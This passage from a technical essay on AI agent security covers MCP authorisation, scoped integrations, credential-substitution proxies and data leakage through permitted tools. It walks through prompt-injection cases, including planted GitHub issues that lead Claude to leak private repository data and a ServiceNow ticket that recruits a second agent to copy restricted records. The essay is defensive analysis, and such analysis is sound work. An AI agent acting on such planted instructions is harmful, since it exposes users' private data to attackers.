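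Cleaning keeps more of the formatting than a ban on images does, but it is easy to get wrong. EchoLeak got past a cleaner that missed one style of link, SearchLeak got past one that ran too late, and Rehberger's fonts got past one that checked only for images. A cleaner that permits a short list of harmless elements, such as headings, bold text and tables, is safer than one that searches for dangerous ones. Reddy and Gujral recommend this kind of restricted Markdown, though they didn't test it or the other defences they list.

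The cleaner also has to work while the answer is still arriving. It can hold back each piece of markup until it is complete, or treat everything as plain text until it has checked the markup. Either approach may slightly delay the formatting.

### What a click still leaks

The remaining remedy is to show links without loading anything until the user clicks. This stops silent leaks and gives the user a chance to notice something odd. But a click sends the same request as an automatic load. If the model has put a login code in the link, the attacker receives the code when the user clicks, along with the user's IP address and some details of the browser.

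A link may read "check-in details" while its address contains half the text of an email. Showing the full address helps only users who read it, and encoded data looks much like the tracking codes in ordinary newsletter links. According to Embrace The Red, an attacker can also hide data in a link with invisible characters. Embrace The Red also describes how Google Colab, a programming tool, sends links through a Google address meant to display a confirmation page first. Such a page shows the destination, but the user still has to decide whether the text after the host name is harmless.

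A product can reduce this leak by applying Anthropic's rule for page fetches to clickable links. If the model added a login code to an address, that address would then appear as plain text. An attacker could still supply many links and have the model pick one, but a click on that link would usually reveal far less than a click on an address the model had written.

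## Replacing web requests with named operations under their own authorisation

Allowlists, address rules and output cleaning all start with a web request and check where it may go. A scoped integration doesn't need that check, because the model only names an operation and fills in a few values, and code a developer wrote beforehand builds the request.

### What the developer settles and what the model still chooses

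Before the model reads anything, the developer of a scoped integration has settled:

- the destination, which is part of the code and which no input can change
- the operations, so that a booking integration can look up a reservation but not cancel it, even if the booking service allows both
- the type of each input, such as a date, an eight-digit number or a choice from a list
- the account, because the integration adds its own token to every request

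Fixing the account would have stopped the uploads to Anthropic's file storage, which depended on the attacker's API key.

The model still decides whether to call the operation, how often, and with what values. The amount of data it can leak this way depends mostly on the type of input. An eight-digit number carries at most log₂ 10⁸ ≈ 27 bits, and only the booking company receives it, while a 4,000-character text field can hold a whole email.

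In MCP, a server is the program that offers the operations, and a client is the part of the AI application that connects to it. *Exposed by Design* (Padilla, 2026) explains that each tool on a server has a name, a description for the model to read, and a schema that defines its inputs. A model can still produce a value that breaks the schema, so the server has to check what it receives.

An MCP server isn't a scoped integration if its one tool can open any address, because the model then has open-ended web access again. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, lists research agents that can connect to any outside domain as an example of excessive permission.

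### Posting a weekly report both ways

Suppose an agent writes a sales report every Friday from a spreadsheet and the week's customer emails, and posts it to a team channel on Slack. Anyone can email the company, so an attacker can plant instructions in an email the agent reads.

With open web access, the developer gives the agent a tool that can send any request to any address, a Slack token, and instructions for posting a message. The model writes the report, then composes a request to Slack containing the token, the channel and the text. Only the developer's instructions restrict the model to that address and channel.

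With a scoped integration, the agent has a single operation for this job, `post_report`, which takes a channel and a text:

1. The model writes the report and calls `post_report`, naming one of three permitted channels.
2. The integration checks the channel against a list in its own settings, which the model can't edit, and checks the length of the text.
3. The integration adds the token for the company's workspace and sends the message to Slack's fixed address.

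The table assumes that the model obeys the planted instruction and has no other tools for sending anything.

| What the planted instruction asks for | Open web access | `post_report` only |
|---|---|---|
| Send the spreadsheet to a stranger's server | Works | Fails, because the operation takes no address |
| Contact a service on the company's internal network | Works if the network allows it | Fails for the same reason |
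| Post to the attacker's own Slack workspace | Works with the attacker's token | Fails, because the integration adds the company's token |
| Post in a different company channel | Works wherever the token allows | Fails the channel check |
| Delete older messages | Works if the token allows | Fails, because there is no such operation |
| Put false sales figures in the report | Works | Works |
| Copy a confidential email into the report | Works | Works, and everyone in the channel can read it |
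| Post the report fifty times | Works | Works unless the integration limits the rate |

An allowlist containing only Slack's address would not have stopped the post to the attacker's workspace, since both workspaces are on the same service.

Although the integration hardly limits how much the model can write, it does limit who can read it. The developer therefore has to check who belongs to each channel and leave out any that customers or contractors have joined. A link in the report can also leak data when Slack fetches a preview.

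Slack's own permissions only partly restrict where an integration can post. According to Slack, its official MCP server can send messages to any type of conversation with the `chat:write` scope. A scope is a permission that limits what a token can do, and this one allows sending messages without limiting the channel. Slack's *chat:write.public scope* describes an additional scope that an app needs to post in channels it hasn't joined, so an app's channel membership can partly limit where it posts. Slack's incoming webhooks are narrower because Slack ties each one to a single channel when a user installs the app.

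A developer can also enforce a list of channels in the MCP server. Glama's *Slack MCP Server* describes a community-built server with a setting for this. The setting restricts only sending, and it is empty by default, which permits every channel.

### How MCP authorises a connection

MCP bases its authorisation on OAuth, the standard behind the pages where users let one online service use their account on another. The user signs in on a page run by an authorisation server, and the application gets an access token instead of a password. The authorisation server may belong to the service or to another organisation, such as the company that manages an employer's logins.

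Suppose the reporting agent's application is connecting to a remote MCP server for the first time. Under the rules in Model Context Protocol's *Authorization*, the connection goes like this:

1. The client sends a request without a token. The server refuses it with status code 401 and points to a public document about itself. The refusal should also name the scopes that the request needs.
2. The client fetches the document, which lists the authorisation servers that the MCP server trusts. It picks one and fetches that server's description to learn where to send the user.
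3. The client identifies itself. If the authorisation server has never dealt with this application, the client can give a web address that leads to a description of it.
4. The client opens the authorisation server's page in the user's browser. Its request names the scopes it wants and the one MCP server where it will use the token. The user signs in and consents.
5. The browser returns to the client with a one-time code. The client exchanges the code for an access token, naming the MCP server again.
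6. The client repeats its original request with the token attached. The MCP server checks that the token is valid and that the authorisation server issued it for this particular server. It does so on every later request too.
7. If the agent later attempts something the token doesn't cover, the server replies with status code 403 and should name the missing scopes. The client asks the user for further consent, gets a new token and tries again. This is called step-up authorisation.

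Someone who intercepts the one-time code can't use it without a secret that only the client has. The client generates this random secret before step 4 and sends the authorisation server only a hash, from which the secret can't feasibly be recovered. In step 5 the client has to produce the secret itself.

Naming the MCP server in steps 4 and 5 produces an audience-bound token, which works only at that server. Without this binding, a malicious MCP server could take a token it received and use it at any other server that trusts the same authorisation server and checks tokens carelessly. Dissanayaka (2026), in *The Anatomy of MCP Authorization*, considers this the most common exploit in real deployments. Clients must always name the MCP server, but some authorisation servers ignore the name, and the binding gives no protection if the MCP server doesn't check it.

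The choice of scopes is less strict. If the refusal in step 1 doesn't name any, the client requests every scope in the server's public document. That document should include only a basic set, but the Model Context Protocol's security guidance lists publishing all possible scopes as a common mistake, which leads these clients to request them all at once.

In step 7 of the step-up procedure, the client requests the new scopes together with all the ones it requested before, so that it doesn't lose permissions it still needs. Permissions can therefore build up over a long task, and the procedure has no step for giving them back. The guidance also recommends that servers ask for related scopes together, which reduces interruptions but makes the token broader.

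The procedure creates a small SSRF risk because in step 2 the client fetches addresses that the MCP server supplied. A malicious server could supply the address of a cloud metadata endpoint. The guidance advises blocking internal addresses and, for clients that run on a company's servers, using an egress proxy.

### Why a server must not pass the token on

Many MCP servers have to call other services. The reporting agent's MCP server, for example, might store charts with a file service. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* requires the server to obtain a separate token from the authorisation server that the file service uses. It forbids the server from forwarding the token it received from the client, even though that would be the easiest way to get access.

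Forwarding a token works only if the file service accepts tokens meant for another service. An attacker who broke into any server that handles such tokens could then use them at the file service. The client could also send its token directly to the file service and bypass the MCP server's limits, including its list of channels. The file service's log could show the wrong identity for each request, which would make a theft harder to investigate. Forwarding can also make the MCP server a confused deputy if the file service assumes that the MCP server has already checked the token.

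Obtaining a separate token creates a risk that an attacker gains access without the user's consent. An MCP server often uses one fixed identity with the other service for all its clients. Once the user has approved that identity, the service may leave a cookie in the browser and skip the consent page next time. An attacker can then register a client with the MCP server and send the user a link that starts a new authorisation. If the user clicks it, no consent page appears, and the resulting authorisation code for the MCP server goes to the attacker. To prevent this, the MCP server must ask for the user's consent separately for each client that registers itself.

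### What the July 2026 revision changed

The first MCP specification, in November 2024, had no authorisation requirements for remote servers. OAuth arrived in March 2025, and audience-bound tokens followed that June. The latest revision is dated 28 July 2026, and Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) lists several changes to authorisation:

- Clients must check which authorisation server a reply came from, whenever the reply names one, before they exchange the one-time code.
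- Clients must store the credentials that identify them separately for each authorisation server and never use them with another.
- Dynamic Client Registration, in which an application registers itself automatically with an authorisation server, is now deprecated. Its replacement is the web address described in step 3.

The check on replies prevents a mix-up attack, in which a malicious authorisation server gets the client to hand over a code that an honest server issued. However, it is recommended but not required that authorisation servers identify themselves in their replies. If an honest server neither does so nor advertises that it will, the client skips the check. The maintainers expect to make identification compulsory in a future revision.

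The replacement for Dynamic Client Registration is also open to impersonation. The web address proves who controls a domain, but a program on the user's own computer can give another application's address and receive the authorisation code meant for that application. Authorisation servers must therefore show the user where the code will go. Dynamic Client Registration will remain available for at least twelve months.

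The biggest change in the Model Context Protocol (MCP) revision, which has little to do with permission, is that MCP no longer keeps sessions, so each request carries everything the server needs to process it. Each request to a remote server also has to name the method and tool in its headers, which gateways can use to decide what to allow, according to the protocol's July 2026 announcement. A company's decrypting proxy could let `post_report` through and refuse every other tool on the same server without parsing the request body.

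Tabata (2026), in *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28*, describes the revision as a clarification of established OAuth practice. This seems more accurate than Dissanayaka's description of it as a decisive hardening of security, because the Model Context Protocol's previous revision already required audience checks and banned token passthrough.

Authorisation is still optional in MCP, so a server that lets anyone use its tools can comply with the protocol. Remote servers that support authorisation should follow the procedure above. Servers that run on the user's own machine and communicate directly with the client should instead take their credentials from the environment they run in.

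### What separate authorisation buys

Giving each integration its own token limits someone who steals one to a single service, whereas a shared token for a company's mail, files and chat would expose all three. In the reporting example, the ban on passthrough reduces the loss further, because a thief can use the client's token only at the MCP server, which still applies the list of channels. A thief with the MCP server's Slack token could go directly to Slack, where only the token's scopes would apply, so those should be narrow as well.

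Separate tokens are also easier to revoke. A company that suspects a problem with its reporting integration can revoke that integration's token and leave the mail connection working. Revoking one broad token would interrupt everything that depends on it, which gives people a reason to delay.

Administrators can also decide on each connection separately. Slack accepts MCP connections only from apps with a fixed identity that are either published in its marketplace or internal to the company, and workspace administrators can approve and manage them. Slack associates each request with the app that made it and keeps audit logs of MCP activity, so an investigator can tell the reporting agent's posts from another app's. Narrow scopes make these logs more useful, because a token with one scope for everything reveals little about what each operation was for.

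When employees authorise connections individually, their employer may have no central record of them, and someone may connect a personal account to a work tool by mistake. Model Context Protocol's *Enterprise-Managed Authorization* describes an optional extension, released by the protocol's maintainers, that moves the decision to the company's login system. An employee signs in once, and the login system applies the company's rules for that employee's group before the client can get a token for each MCP server. Administrators can also cut off access centrally, although a token that a server has already received may keep working until it expires.

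Under this arrangement, employees no longer see a consent page for each server, which saves them many clicks but makes the administrators' choices matter more. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) reports that Claude's directory lists more than 950 MCP servers, and an administrator can connect one for a whole organisation.

Separate tokens protect much less against an attacker who controls the model than against one who steals a token, because the client holds a valid token for each integration and uses the right one whenever the model makes a call. *MCP-38* notes that an attacker who manipulates an agent gains the combined abilities of all the tools loaded at the same time. So the reporting agent shouldn't have a mail-sending tool in the same session just because the company has approved one.

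### What a valid token doesn't show

Suppose a planted email gets the agent to report falsely that sales fell by half. The call passes every check in the Slack integration because it uses a permitted operation, a permitted channel and a valid token. The token shows that the application may post reports, but nobody asked the user to approve this one.

Under OAuth, the user consents when the token is granted, and the agent may then make hundreds of calls. Dissanayaka points out that OAuth can confirm that a permission is valid, but not that the agent had good reason to use it. Shorter-lived tokens don't solve this, because a client can often renew them without asking the user again.

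Step-up consent gives the user another chance to object, but an attacker can trigger the request. If text planted in an email tells the agent to delete files, the server refuses because the agent lacks the scope, and the user then sees a consent page from the real service asking for permission to delete. That page may not mention the email. Claude Code's users approved nearly all of its permission prompts, so many people would probably approve this one too.

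Asking the user about the particular action works better. Under the July revision, a server can answer a call by requesting more information, and the client repeats the call with the user's reply. Supabase, a database company, plans to use this to confirm queries that would delete data. For the weekly report, the client could show the finished text and the channel before posting, though the user would still have to notice that the sales figures were wrong.

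### How common excessive permissions are

Developers often grant more access than a job requires. *MCP-38* gives the example of a tool that summarises email but can also delete and send it. It also describes servers that request more scopes as they add features and keep those scopes after dropping the features.

There is evidence that both developers and AI agents often choose broader privileges than a task needs. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (2026) cites a study in which 99.8 percent of 447,000 automated workflows on GitHub had more privileges than they needed. These were ordinary programming workflows, so the figure shows how developers set permissions, not how AI integrations behave. The paper also cites a test of 11 language-model agents across 544 scenarios. Six of the agents chose a tool with excessive privileges more than 30 percent of the time, even though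 a more limited tool would have been enough. A developer who provides both a broad tool and a narrow one therefore can't count on the model to pick the narrow one.

*SkillScope* (2026) studied skills, which are packages of instructions and code that people add to agents. It found that excessive privilege is widespread in third-party skills. Some collected more data than the user's task required, and slightly more took actions the task didn't call for.

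Finding the narrowest scope isn't always easy. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) examined the scopes for 517 Google services. Google's catalogue may list several scopes for an operation, any one of which is enough, and leaves the choice to the developer. If each of two scopes permits something the other doesn't, neither is narrower, and the developer has to decide which extra permission would do less harm.

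Even when a narrow option is available, most people don't use it. A March 2026 Model Context Protocol post reports that about 17 percent of users enable the read-only mode of GitHub's integration.

### How common weak and untrustworthy servers are

Zhou, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers*, found 7,973 live servers on the public internet. About 41 percent let anyone use their tools without authentication, 29 percent relied on fixed keys, and 30 percent used OAuth. Most of the open servers the team sampled were tests or demonstrations with no sensitive data, but one let anyone search more than 5,000 customer records.

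The team then tested 119 of the servers that used OAuth, and every one had at least one flaw. About 97 percent had flaws in Dynamic Client Registration, which helps explain why MCP has since deprecated it. The tested servers were probably weaker than average, because the team could test only servers that let new clients register themselves, and it left out 316 where strict company controls kept it from completing the tests.

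Padilla tested 414 servers in July 2026 and found that 92 percent lacked OAuth. That share is higher than in the other study, perhaps because servers that require a sign-in are harder for an outsider to test. A server without OAuth may still require a key. Padilla also found 68 vulnerabilities worth reporting, including SSRF against cloud metadata endpoints. Across a wider set of 640 servers, 687 tools could run shell commands without access controls. An agent connected to one of those tools could have open-ended web access through the server, even if the agent's own network blocks outbound requests.

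A server that requires a sign-in can still apply its access rules badly. *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile* (2026) examined 6,137 MCP servers and found that 46 percent didn't correctly check authorisation every time somebody used a tool.

These studies measure carelessness, not how many servers are malicious. Publishing a malicious server would be easy. *A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol* (2025) counted 67,057 servers across six public registries, five of which let users submit their own. A malicious server could plant instructions in its tool descriptions, or behave well until the user has approved it and then change what its tools do. It can also label a tool that deletes files as read-only. The protocol's maintainers warn that such labels are only hints, and that most clients trust a server once someone has installed it.

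None of these figures is weighted by use, and a company that connects only to the official servers of Slack and its other suppliers faces much less risk than they suggest. But it still relies on each server's code to contact only its stated destination. This matters particularly for servers that run on the user's machine, usually with little isolation. *We Urgently Need Privilege Management in MCP* (2025) found that 1,438 of 2,562 MCP plugins used network functions. Many need network access to do their work, but a plugin meant to contact one service could also contact an attacker's server. An operator can prevent this by running the plugin in a sandbox whose egress proxy permits only the intended service.

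## Keeping credentials out of the model's reach

The list of channels in `post_report` works only because the model never has the Slack token. If the token were in the model's context, or in a file that its code could open, planted text could get the model to send the token to an attacker, who could then call Slack from any computer. Only the token's scopes and expiry date would limit those calls, because they would bypass both the channel list and the egress proxy.

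Most keys are bearer secrets, so anyone who holds one can use it. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) points out that a service that receives a static API key can't distinguish the intended agent from a compromised one.

### How keys end up where the model can read them

Coding agents usually inherit the credentials already on the developer's machine. *Agent Authenticator* (2026) lists SSH keys, GitHub tokens, cloud logins and tokens for publishing packages as examples. Many agent frameworks also encourage developers to keep API keys in unencrypted environment variables, according to *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026). Programs that the agent starts can normally read these variables.

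Keys also reach the model by accident. *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (Chen, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) identified 520 skills with credential leaks. About 90 percent of the leaked credentials were immediately exploitable. Debug logging accounted for 73.5 percent of the vulnerabilities. In an ordinary program, a key printed during testing appears on the developer's screen, but agent frameworks feed printed output into the model's context.

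Once a key is in the conversation, it is hard to remove. *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues, 2026) traces how the software copies it into the chat history, logs, stored memories and generated code. Deleting the original message leaves those copies in place, so the owner has to revoke the key.

### Credential substitution, step by step

The usual remedy is to give the sandbox a placeholder and have the egress proxy swap in the real key. Suppose a coding agent needs to read bug reports from a company's private GitHub project:

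1. The operator stores the GitHub key outside the sandbox and records which hosts may receive it. Inside the sandbox, the variable that would normally hold the key contains a meaningless placeholder.
2. The agent runs an ordinary GitHub program, which puts the placeholder in the request's `Authorization` header, the field where services usually expect a key.
3. The request leaves the sandbox and reaches the proxy, which decrypts it.
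4. The proxy checks that the network rules permit the destination and that this key may go there.
5. The proxy replaces the placeholder with the real key, encrypts the request again and forwards it to GitHub.
6. GitHub's reply comes back through the proxy to the agent.

If planted text causes the agent to print its credentials or send them to a stranger, the agent reveals only a placeholder that no service accepts.

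The sandbox has to trust the proxy's certificate for this to work. Anthropic's *Securely deploying AI agents* describes an alternative that avoids decryption. The agent calls a tool that runs outside the sandbox and makes the authenticated request. `post_report` works this way. Substitution is more useful when the agent has to run existing command-line programs that expect a key.

### How OpenAI and Docker do it

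OpenAI's hosted shell tool runs the model's commands in a container on OpenAI's servers. The container has no network access by default. An administrator has to approve domains for the whole organisation, and the developer then lists the ones that a particular request needs. The developer also supplies any credentials, which OpenAI's *Shell* calls "domain secrets", each with a domain, a name and a value. The model and container receive only a placeholder such as `$API_KEY`. According to *From model to agent* (Xu, Zhang and Arunachalam, 2026), all outbound requests pass through a proxy beside the container, which replaces the placeholder with the real value only for approved destinations.

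Docker's local sandboxes each run in a small virtual machine on the user's computer, and the proxy runs outside the virtual machine. Docker's *Manage credentials* says the real key normally stays in the computer's keychain. For services with built-in support, such as GitHub, the proxy overwrites whatever the agent put in the authentication header. For other services, users can set up a custom secret, which works more like OpenAI's because the proxy replaces a placeholder with the real key.

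Other companies have adopted the same pattern. Cloudflare (2026) offers it for its sandboxes, and Anthropic offers it for the agents it hosts.

### Keys that come back in the reply

A service may repeat the key in its reply, for instance in an error message that quotes the request's headers. The key will then reach the model unless something filters the reply. An example in OpenAI's guide sends a dummy key to `httpbin.org`, a testing site that returns the headers it receives, and asks the model to report what it receives. The guide doesn't describe a filter.

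Docker's proxy filters replies to requests in which it inserted a custom secret. It masks the secret in its original form and in three common encodings, and it blocks partial replies, which could deliver the secret in pieces. Docker warns that the filter doesn't inspect WebSocket messages (a format for continuous two-way connections) and would miss a secret that the service split across several fields. Never approving a host that echoes headers is safer, though an operator may not know what every error message contains.

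Kenney and colleagues tested a related risk in a product from their own company, Corvic. With a GitHub key attached, they sent requests from the sandbox to sites that echo headers, and no key came back. But nobody had approved those sites to receive the key, so the result shows that the destination check worked, not that an approved service would leave the key out of its response.

Some programs send a long-lived key to a service and receive a temporary session token in return. *Authenticate with vaults* warns that Anthropic's proxy changes only outgoing requests, so the new token arrives in the sandbox unmasked. Anthropic advises developers to make the exchange themselves and store the token outside the sandbox.

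### Substitution in the wrong place

A proxy that replaces the placeholder wherever it appears in a request can publish the real credential. Suppose an attacker plants text instructing the agent to copy its GitHub credential into a comment on a public project. The agent has only the placeholder, so it writes that. Because the request goes to GitHub, an approved host, the proxy substitutes the real credential, which anyone can then read in the comment.

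An earlier version of Docker's guide said that the proxy replaced a custom secret's placeholder "anywhere in the request". The current version says that the proxy replaces it only in headers the user has chosen or in Docker's default headers, and sends a placeholder in the body unchanged. Anthropic lets developers choose replacement in headers, the body or both, and recommends headers alone because agents often assemble the body from content they are working with. The default is both, so developers must select headers alone to get this protection.

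The header-only rule breaks services that require the key elsewhere. In one of Kenney and colleagues' tests, an economic data service required the key in the web address, but the proxy had put it in a header. The request failed without leaking the key. Substitution also fails for programs that use the key to compute a signature, as many Amazon cloud clients do, because they sign with the placeholder instead.

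### Ways around the proxy

A program that bypasses the proxy has only the placeholder, so it can't leak the key. It can still leak any other data in the sandbox, because the destination rules no longer apply. To prevent this, all of the sandbox's network traffic should have to go through a proxy. Docker's *Isolation layers* describes a setup that forces all outbound TCP traffic through a proxy and blocks most other kinds by default. Programs that ignore the proxy settings go through a second proxy, which enforces the destination rules but doesn't insert keys. Their requests to private services therefore fail without exposing a key.

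SSH sessions can also carry real API keys into a sandbox. When Docker introduced SSH access to its sandboxes on July 24, 2026, these sessions could copy keys from the user's environment, according to its release notes (Docker, 2026). Docker stopped this by default five days later, and in August it fixed a similar leak of login tokens from Claude's desktop app.

Many projects also keep keys in a file called `.env`, which an agent can read if it has access to the project folder, so the owner has to move those keys elsewhere. An operator can check for remaining keys by searching from inside the sandbox. Kenney and colleagues searched the environment variables and twelve common locations for key files, and found no keys.

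The list of hosts for each key needs the same care. Until November 2026, Docker let users create a custom secret with no destination host. It now substitutes such a secret only after the user names a host (Docker, 2026).

### A key that the attacker supplies

Hiding the user's key doesn't stop an attacker from planting a different one, as in the Claude Cowork uploads. A proxy that only searches for placeholders finds none in a request with the planted key and forwards it to the approved host.

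The proxy should therefore reject or overwrite any credential it didn't supply. Docker's method for known services does this over encrypted connections, at least for the header it overwrites. If an upload carried the attacker's key in that header, the proxy would replace it with the user's key, and the data would end up in the user's own account. If a service accepts keys in several places, the proxy has to cover all of them. Over unencrypted connections, Docker's proxy neither inserts keys nor removes the program's own, so an operator should block unencrypted requests to these services.

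### Short-lived tokens

Substitution makes a key harder to steal, and giving tokens a short life and a narrow scope limits what a thief can do with one. *Security Analysis of Agentic AI Communication Protocols* (2025) describes a travel agent whose token stays valid for hours, so a thief can use it to repeat a hotel booking many times. A token that expired after five minutes would give the thief much less time, although a script could still make many bookings before then.

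The table compares a long-lived, broad key behind a proxy with a short-lived, narrow token that sits in the sandbox.

| Event | Long-lived key behind a proxy | Short-lived token in the sandbox |
|---|---|---|
| Planted text gets the agent to reveal its credentials | The attacker gets a placeholder | The attacker gets a token that works until it expires |
| A service's reply exposes the credential | The attacker may get a key that works for months | The attacker gets a token that works until it expires |
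| The attacker misuses the service through the agent | Anything the key permits | Only what the token's scopes permit |
| A program has to sign requests itself | Fails | Works, if the service issues temporary signing keys |

A product may need both a proxy and narrow tokens. The proxy can hold a short-lived token instead of a permanent key, so that a token leaked through an echoed header soon expires. Programs that can't work with a placeholder can receive a narrow token directly. Claude Cowork takes roughly this approach. It keeps the user's credentials in the computer's keychain and gives the virtual machine a narrower token for one session, which Anthropic can revoke without cancelling the user's own credentials.

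Docker's proxy can get keys from a password manager and by default keeps each one for 55 minutes before fetching it again. Refetching a key doesn't shorten the time it is valid, so a stolen copy still works until the service itself expires or revokes it.

Another option is a token that works only with a private cryptographic key, so an attacker who steals the token alone can't use it. But if both are in the sandbox, an attacker can steal both. *Agent Authenticator* therefore proposes tying an agent's credentials to hardware, from which software can't copy them.

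### Misuse through the proxy

Giving the agent a placeholder instead of the real key does not stop an attacker who controls the agent from using the service through the proxy during the session. The proxy adds the real key to any request that passes its checks, regardless of who initiated it. If the GitHub key allows project deletion, the agent can still delete projects using the placeholder.

Kenney and colleagues scored several threats out of 25 before and after adding their employer's product. The score for a secret pasted into a prompt fell from 25 to 4, but the score for a connection with too many permissions fell only from 20 to 15. These scores are the team's own judgments, not measurements, but the difference makes sense because hiding a key doesn't change what it permits.

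SSH keys have the same problem. By default, Docker gives many sandboxes access to a program on the user's computer that signs data with the user's SSH keys. Code in the sandbox can't read the keys, but it can ask for signatures, so an attacker might get malicious code signed in the developer's name.

The proxy can narrow what an attacker can do. *Caging the Agents* (2026), a design for AI agents in healthcare, limits the number, destinations and size of each agent's requests. The *Credential proxy* guide for fnox, an open-source tool, shows a rule that inserts a GitHub key only into requests that read, create or edit things in one organisation's projects. A request to delete one of those projects would go out without the real key, so it should fail, but an attacker could still rewrite a bug report.

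If the key behind the proxy allows its holder to create more keys, an attacker can have the agent create one, and the service will send it back in a reply. Docker's filter masks only the key it inserted, so it would let the new one through. The attacker could then use the new key from anywhere, even after the operator has shut down the sandbox. The key behind the proxy should therefore not have permission to create others.

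## How data can still leave through an authorised integration

Even when an integration is scoped and its key is hidden, the model still writes the text that the integration sends. For instance, a planted email could get the weekly reporting agent to paste a salary list into its Slack report. Integrations that write comments, support tickets or calendar invitations carry the same risk. The attacker only needs permission to read the place where the text ends up, and doesn't need a server to collect the data.

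The defences described so far would not block this, because the destination, account and operation are all permitted. Rahman and Kim showed that a filter that searches the text for secrets is easy to evade.

### GitHub: private data in a public project

Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) describes a demonstration with GitHub's official MCP server. The test user had several private repositories (a repository holds one project's files) and a public one. The researchers planted instructions in an issue (a bug report or request) in the public repository, where anybody can open an issue.

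The user then asked Claude Opus 4, running in Claude's desktop app, to look at the game's open issues. Claude read the planted issue, fetched data from the private repositories and put it in a pull request (a proposed change to a project's files) on the public repository. Anyone could now read the names of the user's private projects, the user's salary and a plan to move to South America.

Invariant Labs says the server's code was not at fault, so GitHub could not fix the problem by patching the server. The user was entitled to read the private repositories and write to the public one, and the agent had both permissions at once. By default, the desktop app asks the user to confirm each tool call, but many people choose "Always Allow".

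Invariant Labs, which sells security software for agents, recommends limiting an agent to one repository per session. Software between the agent and its tools refuses any call that names a different repository from earlier calls. This rule would have stopped the demonstration when Claude turned to the private repositories. It would also stop a user who wants to copy a fix from one project to another. And because it covers only GitHub, it wouldn't stop an agent from copying the user's email into a public issue.

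### ServiceNow: agents that recruit other agents

ServiceNow makes software that companies use to handle support tickets, and its Now Assist platform adds AI agents. An agent that can't finish a task alone can call on another. By default, agents that a company publishes to the same chat channel join one team and can find each other. Aaron Costello of the security company AppOmni tested how a malicious ticket could exploit this setup.

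Costello used two of ServiceNow's ready-made agents. One reads and summarises tickets, and the other can read, create and update records. The attacker's account could create tickets but could not read other people's. The attack ran as follows:

1. The attacker filed a ticket with planted instructions in its description.
2. An administrator's request led the summarising agent to read the ticket. The planted text told it to copy a restricted ticket's description into this one, and to find another agent if it couldn't do so itself.
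3. The record-updating agent did the copying. It could open the restricted ticket because Now Assist agents normally run with the permissions of whoever started the conversation, in this case the administrator.
4. The attacker opened their own ticket and read the restricted text.

ServiceNow's protection against prompt injection was on throughout. In other tests, Costello got agents to give a malicious user the administrator role and to email records to an outside address. In the ticket attack, the data stayed inside ServiceNow, so an egress proxy would have had nothing to check.

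ServiceNow confirmed to Costello that this behaviour was intended and updated its documentation to explain the risk. TechRadar's *Second-order prompt injection can turn AI into a malicious insider* reports that the company said it would not change the product. In The Hacker News (2025), Costello calls the finding alarming because it is expected behaviour rather than a bug. Customers can change all the settings involved, which supports ServiceNow's position, but few administrators would guess that publishing two agents to one channel lets anyone who can file a ticket direct the more powerful one.

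### How safe connections become unsafe together

An agent combines the properties of all its connections, so two connections that are each fairly safe can together meet Willison's three conditions for data theft. The table shows some examples.

| Connection | Reads private data | Reads outsiders' text | Writes where outsiders can read |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mailbox, read only | Yes | Yes | No |
| Sales spreadsheet, read only | Yes | No | No |
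| Public issue tracker, read and comment | No | Yes | Yes |
| Company blog, publish only | No | No | Yes |
| Mailbox and company blog | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Spreadsheet and issue tracker | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Spreadsheet and company blog | Yes | No | Yes |
| GitHub, with access to the whole account | Yes | Yes | Yes |

Willison points out that GitHub's integration met all three conditions by itself. In Costello's test, the tools to check included those of every agent that the summarising agent could call.

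The answers can also change after approval. Adding a column of customer comments puts outsiders' text in the spreadsheet, and adding a contractor to a Slack channel lets an outsider read it. "Outsider" here means anyone who shouldn't see the data, such as the person with an ordinary account in the ServiceNow case.

### Splitting permissions and fixing recipients

A read-only token would have stopped Claude from opening the pull request. It would also stop an agent from replying to bug reports, which may be the reason for having the agent. The restriction has to hold across everything the agent can reach. ServiceNow's summarising agent couldn't update records, but it could pass the task to an agent that could. AppOmni therefore recommends separate teams, each with only the agents needed for one job. An attacker who plants text can then misuse only that team's tools.

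Some read-only operations also send data out. For example, searching an outside service gives that service the search terms. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* suggests allowing such a tool only when everything the model passes to it is public. Software could recognise these tools by the labels that honest MCP servers attach to them.

A fixed list of recipients works well when the operator knows who they are and what they may see. It would not have helped in the GitHub demonstration, because the data went to the repository the user had asked about, which any sensible list would have included.

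A permitted recipient can also be the wrong one for particular data. In an example from Microsoft, Alex asks an agent to deal with unanswered email. Priya has sent Alex a preview of the quarterly sales figures, and Marco, who isn't allowed to see them yet, has written to ask about them. The agent might answer Marco's question using Priya's figures. Nobody has attacked the agent, and Alex may well write to Marco every day. To prevent this leak, the software has to check who may read the figures as well as who may receive email.

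### Ending write access after the agent reads untrusted text

Willison (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, discusses a paper by eleven researchers from IBM, Google, Microsoft and elsewhere. The paper recommends that once an agent has read untrusted text, the system make it impossible for that text to trigger any consequential action. Under this rule, Claude could not have opened a pull request after reading the public issues, and ServiceNow's agents could not have updated a ticket after reading the attacker's. This has a big advantage over a filter because the software doesn't have to recognise the text as malicious.

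The rule also blocks a lot of ordinary work. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) tested a similar rule on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 tasks in office work, travel, banking and Slack. Without any policy, 152 attacks succeeded against the paper's basic agent, which used GPT-4o. None succeeded when policies restricted the agent's actions after it had read untrusted text and limited where private data could go. But the share of ordinary tasks it completed, averaged over the four areas, fell from about 84 to 42 percent.

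A developer can recover some of this by having the agent write before it reads. Starting a new session for the writing also helps, as long as the software doesn't carry over text from the old one, since even a summary of an untrusted email is untrusted.

### Asking a person to approve

Human approval could have stopped both attacks. AppOmni recommends running any ServiceNow tool that can change records or send email in supervised mode, where the user reviews each action first. Administrators also have to keep one system setting turned off, because it makes an agent with even one unsupervised tool run all its tools unsupervised.

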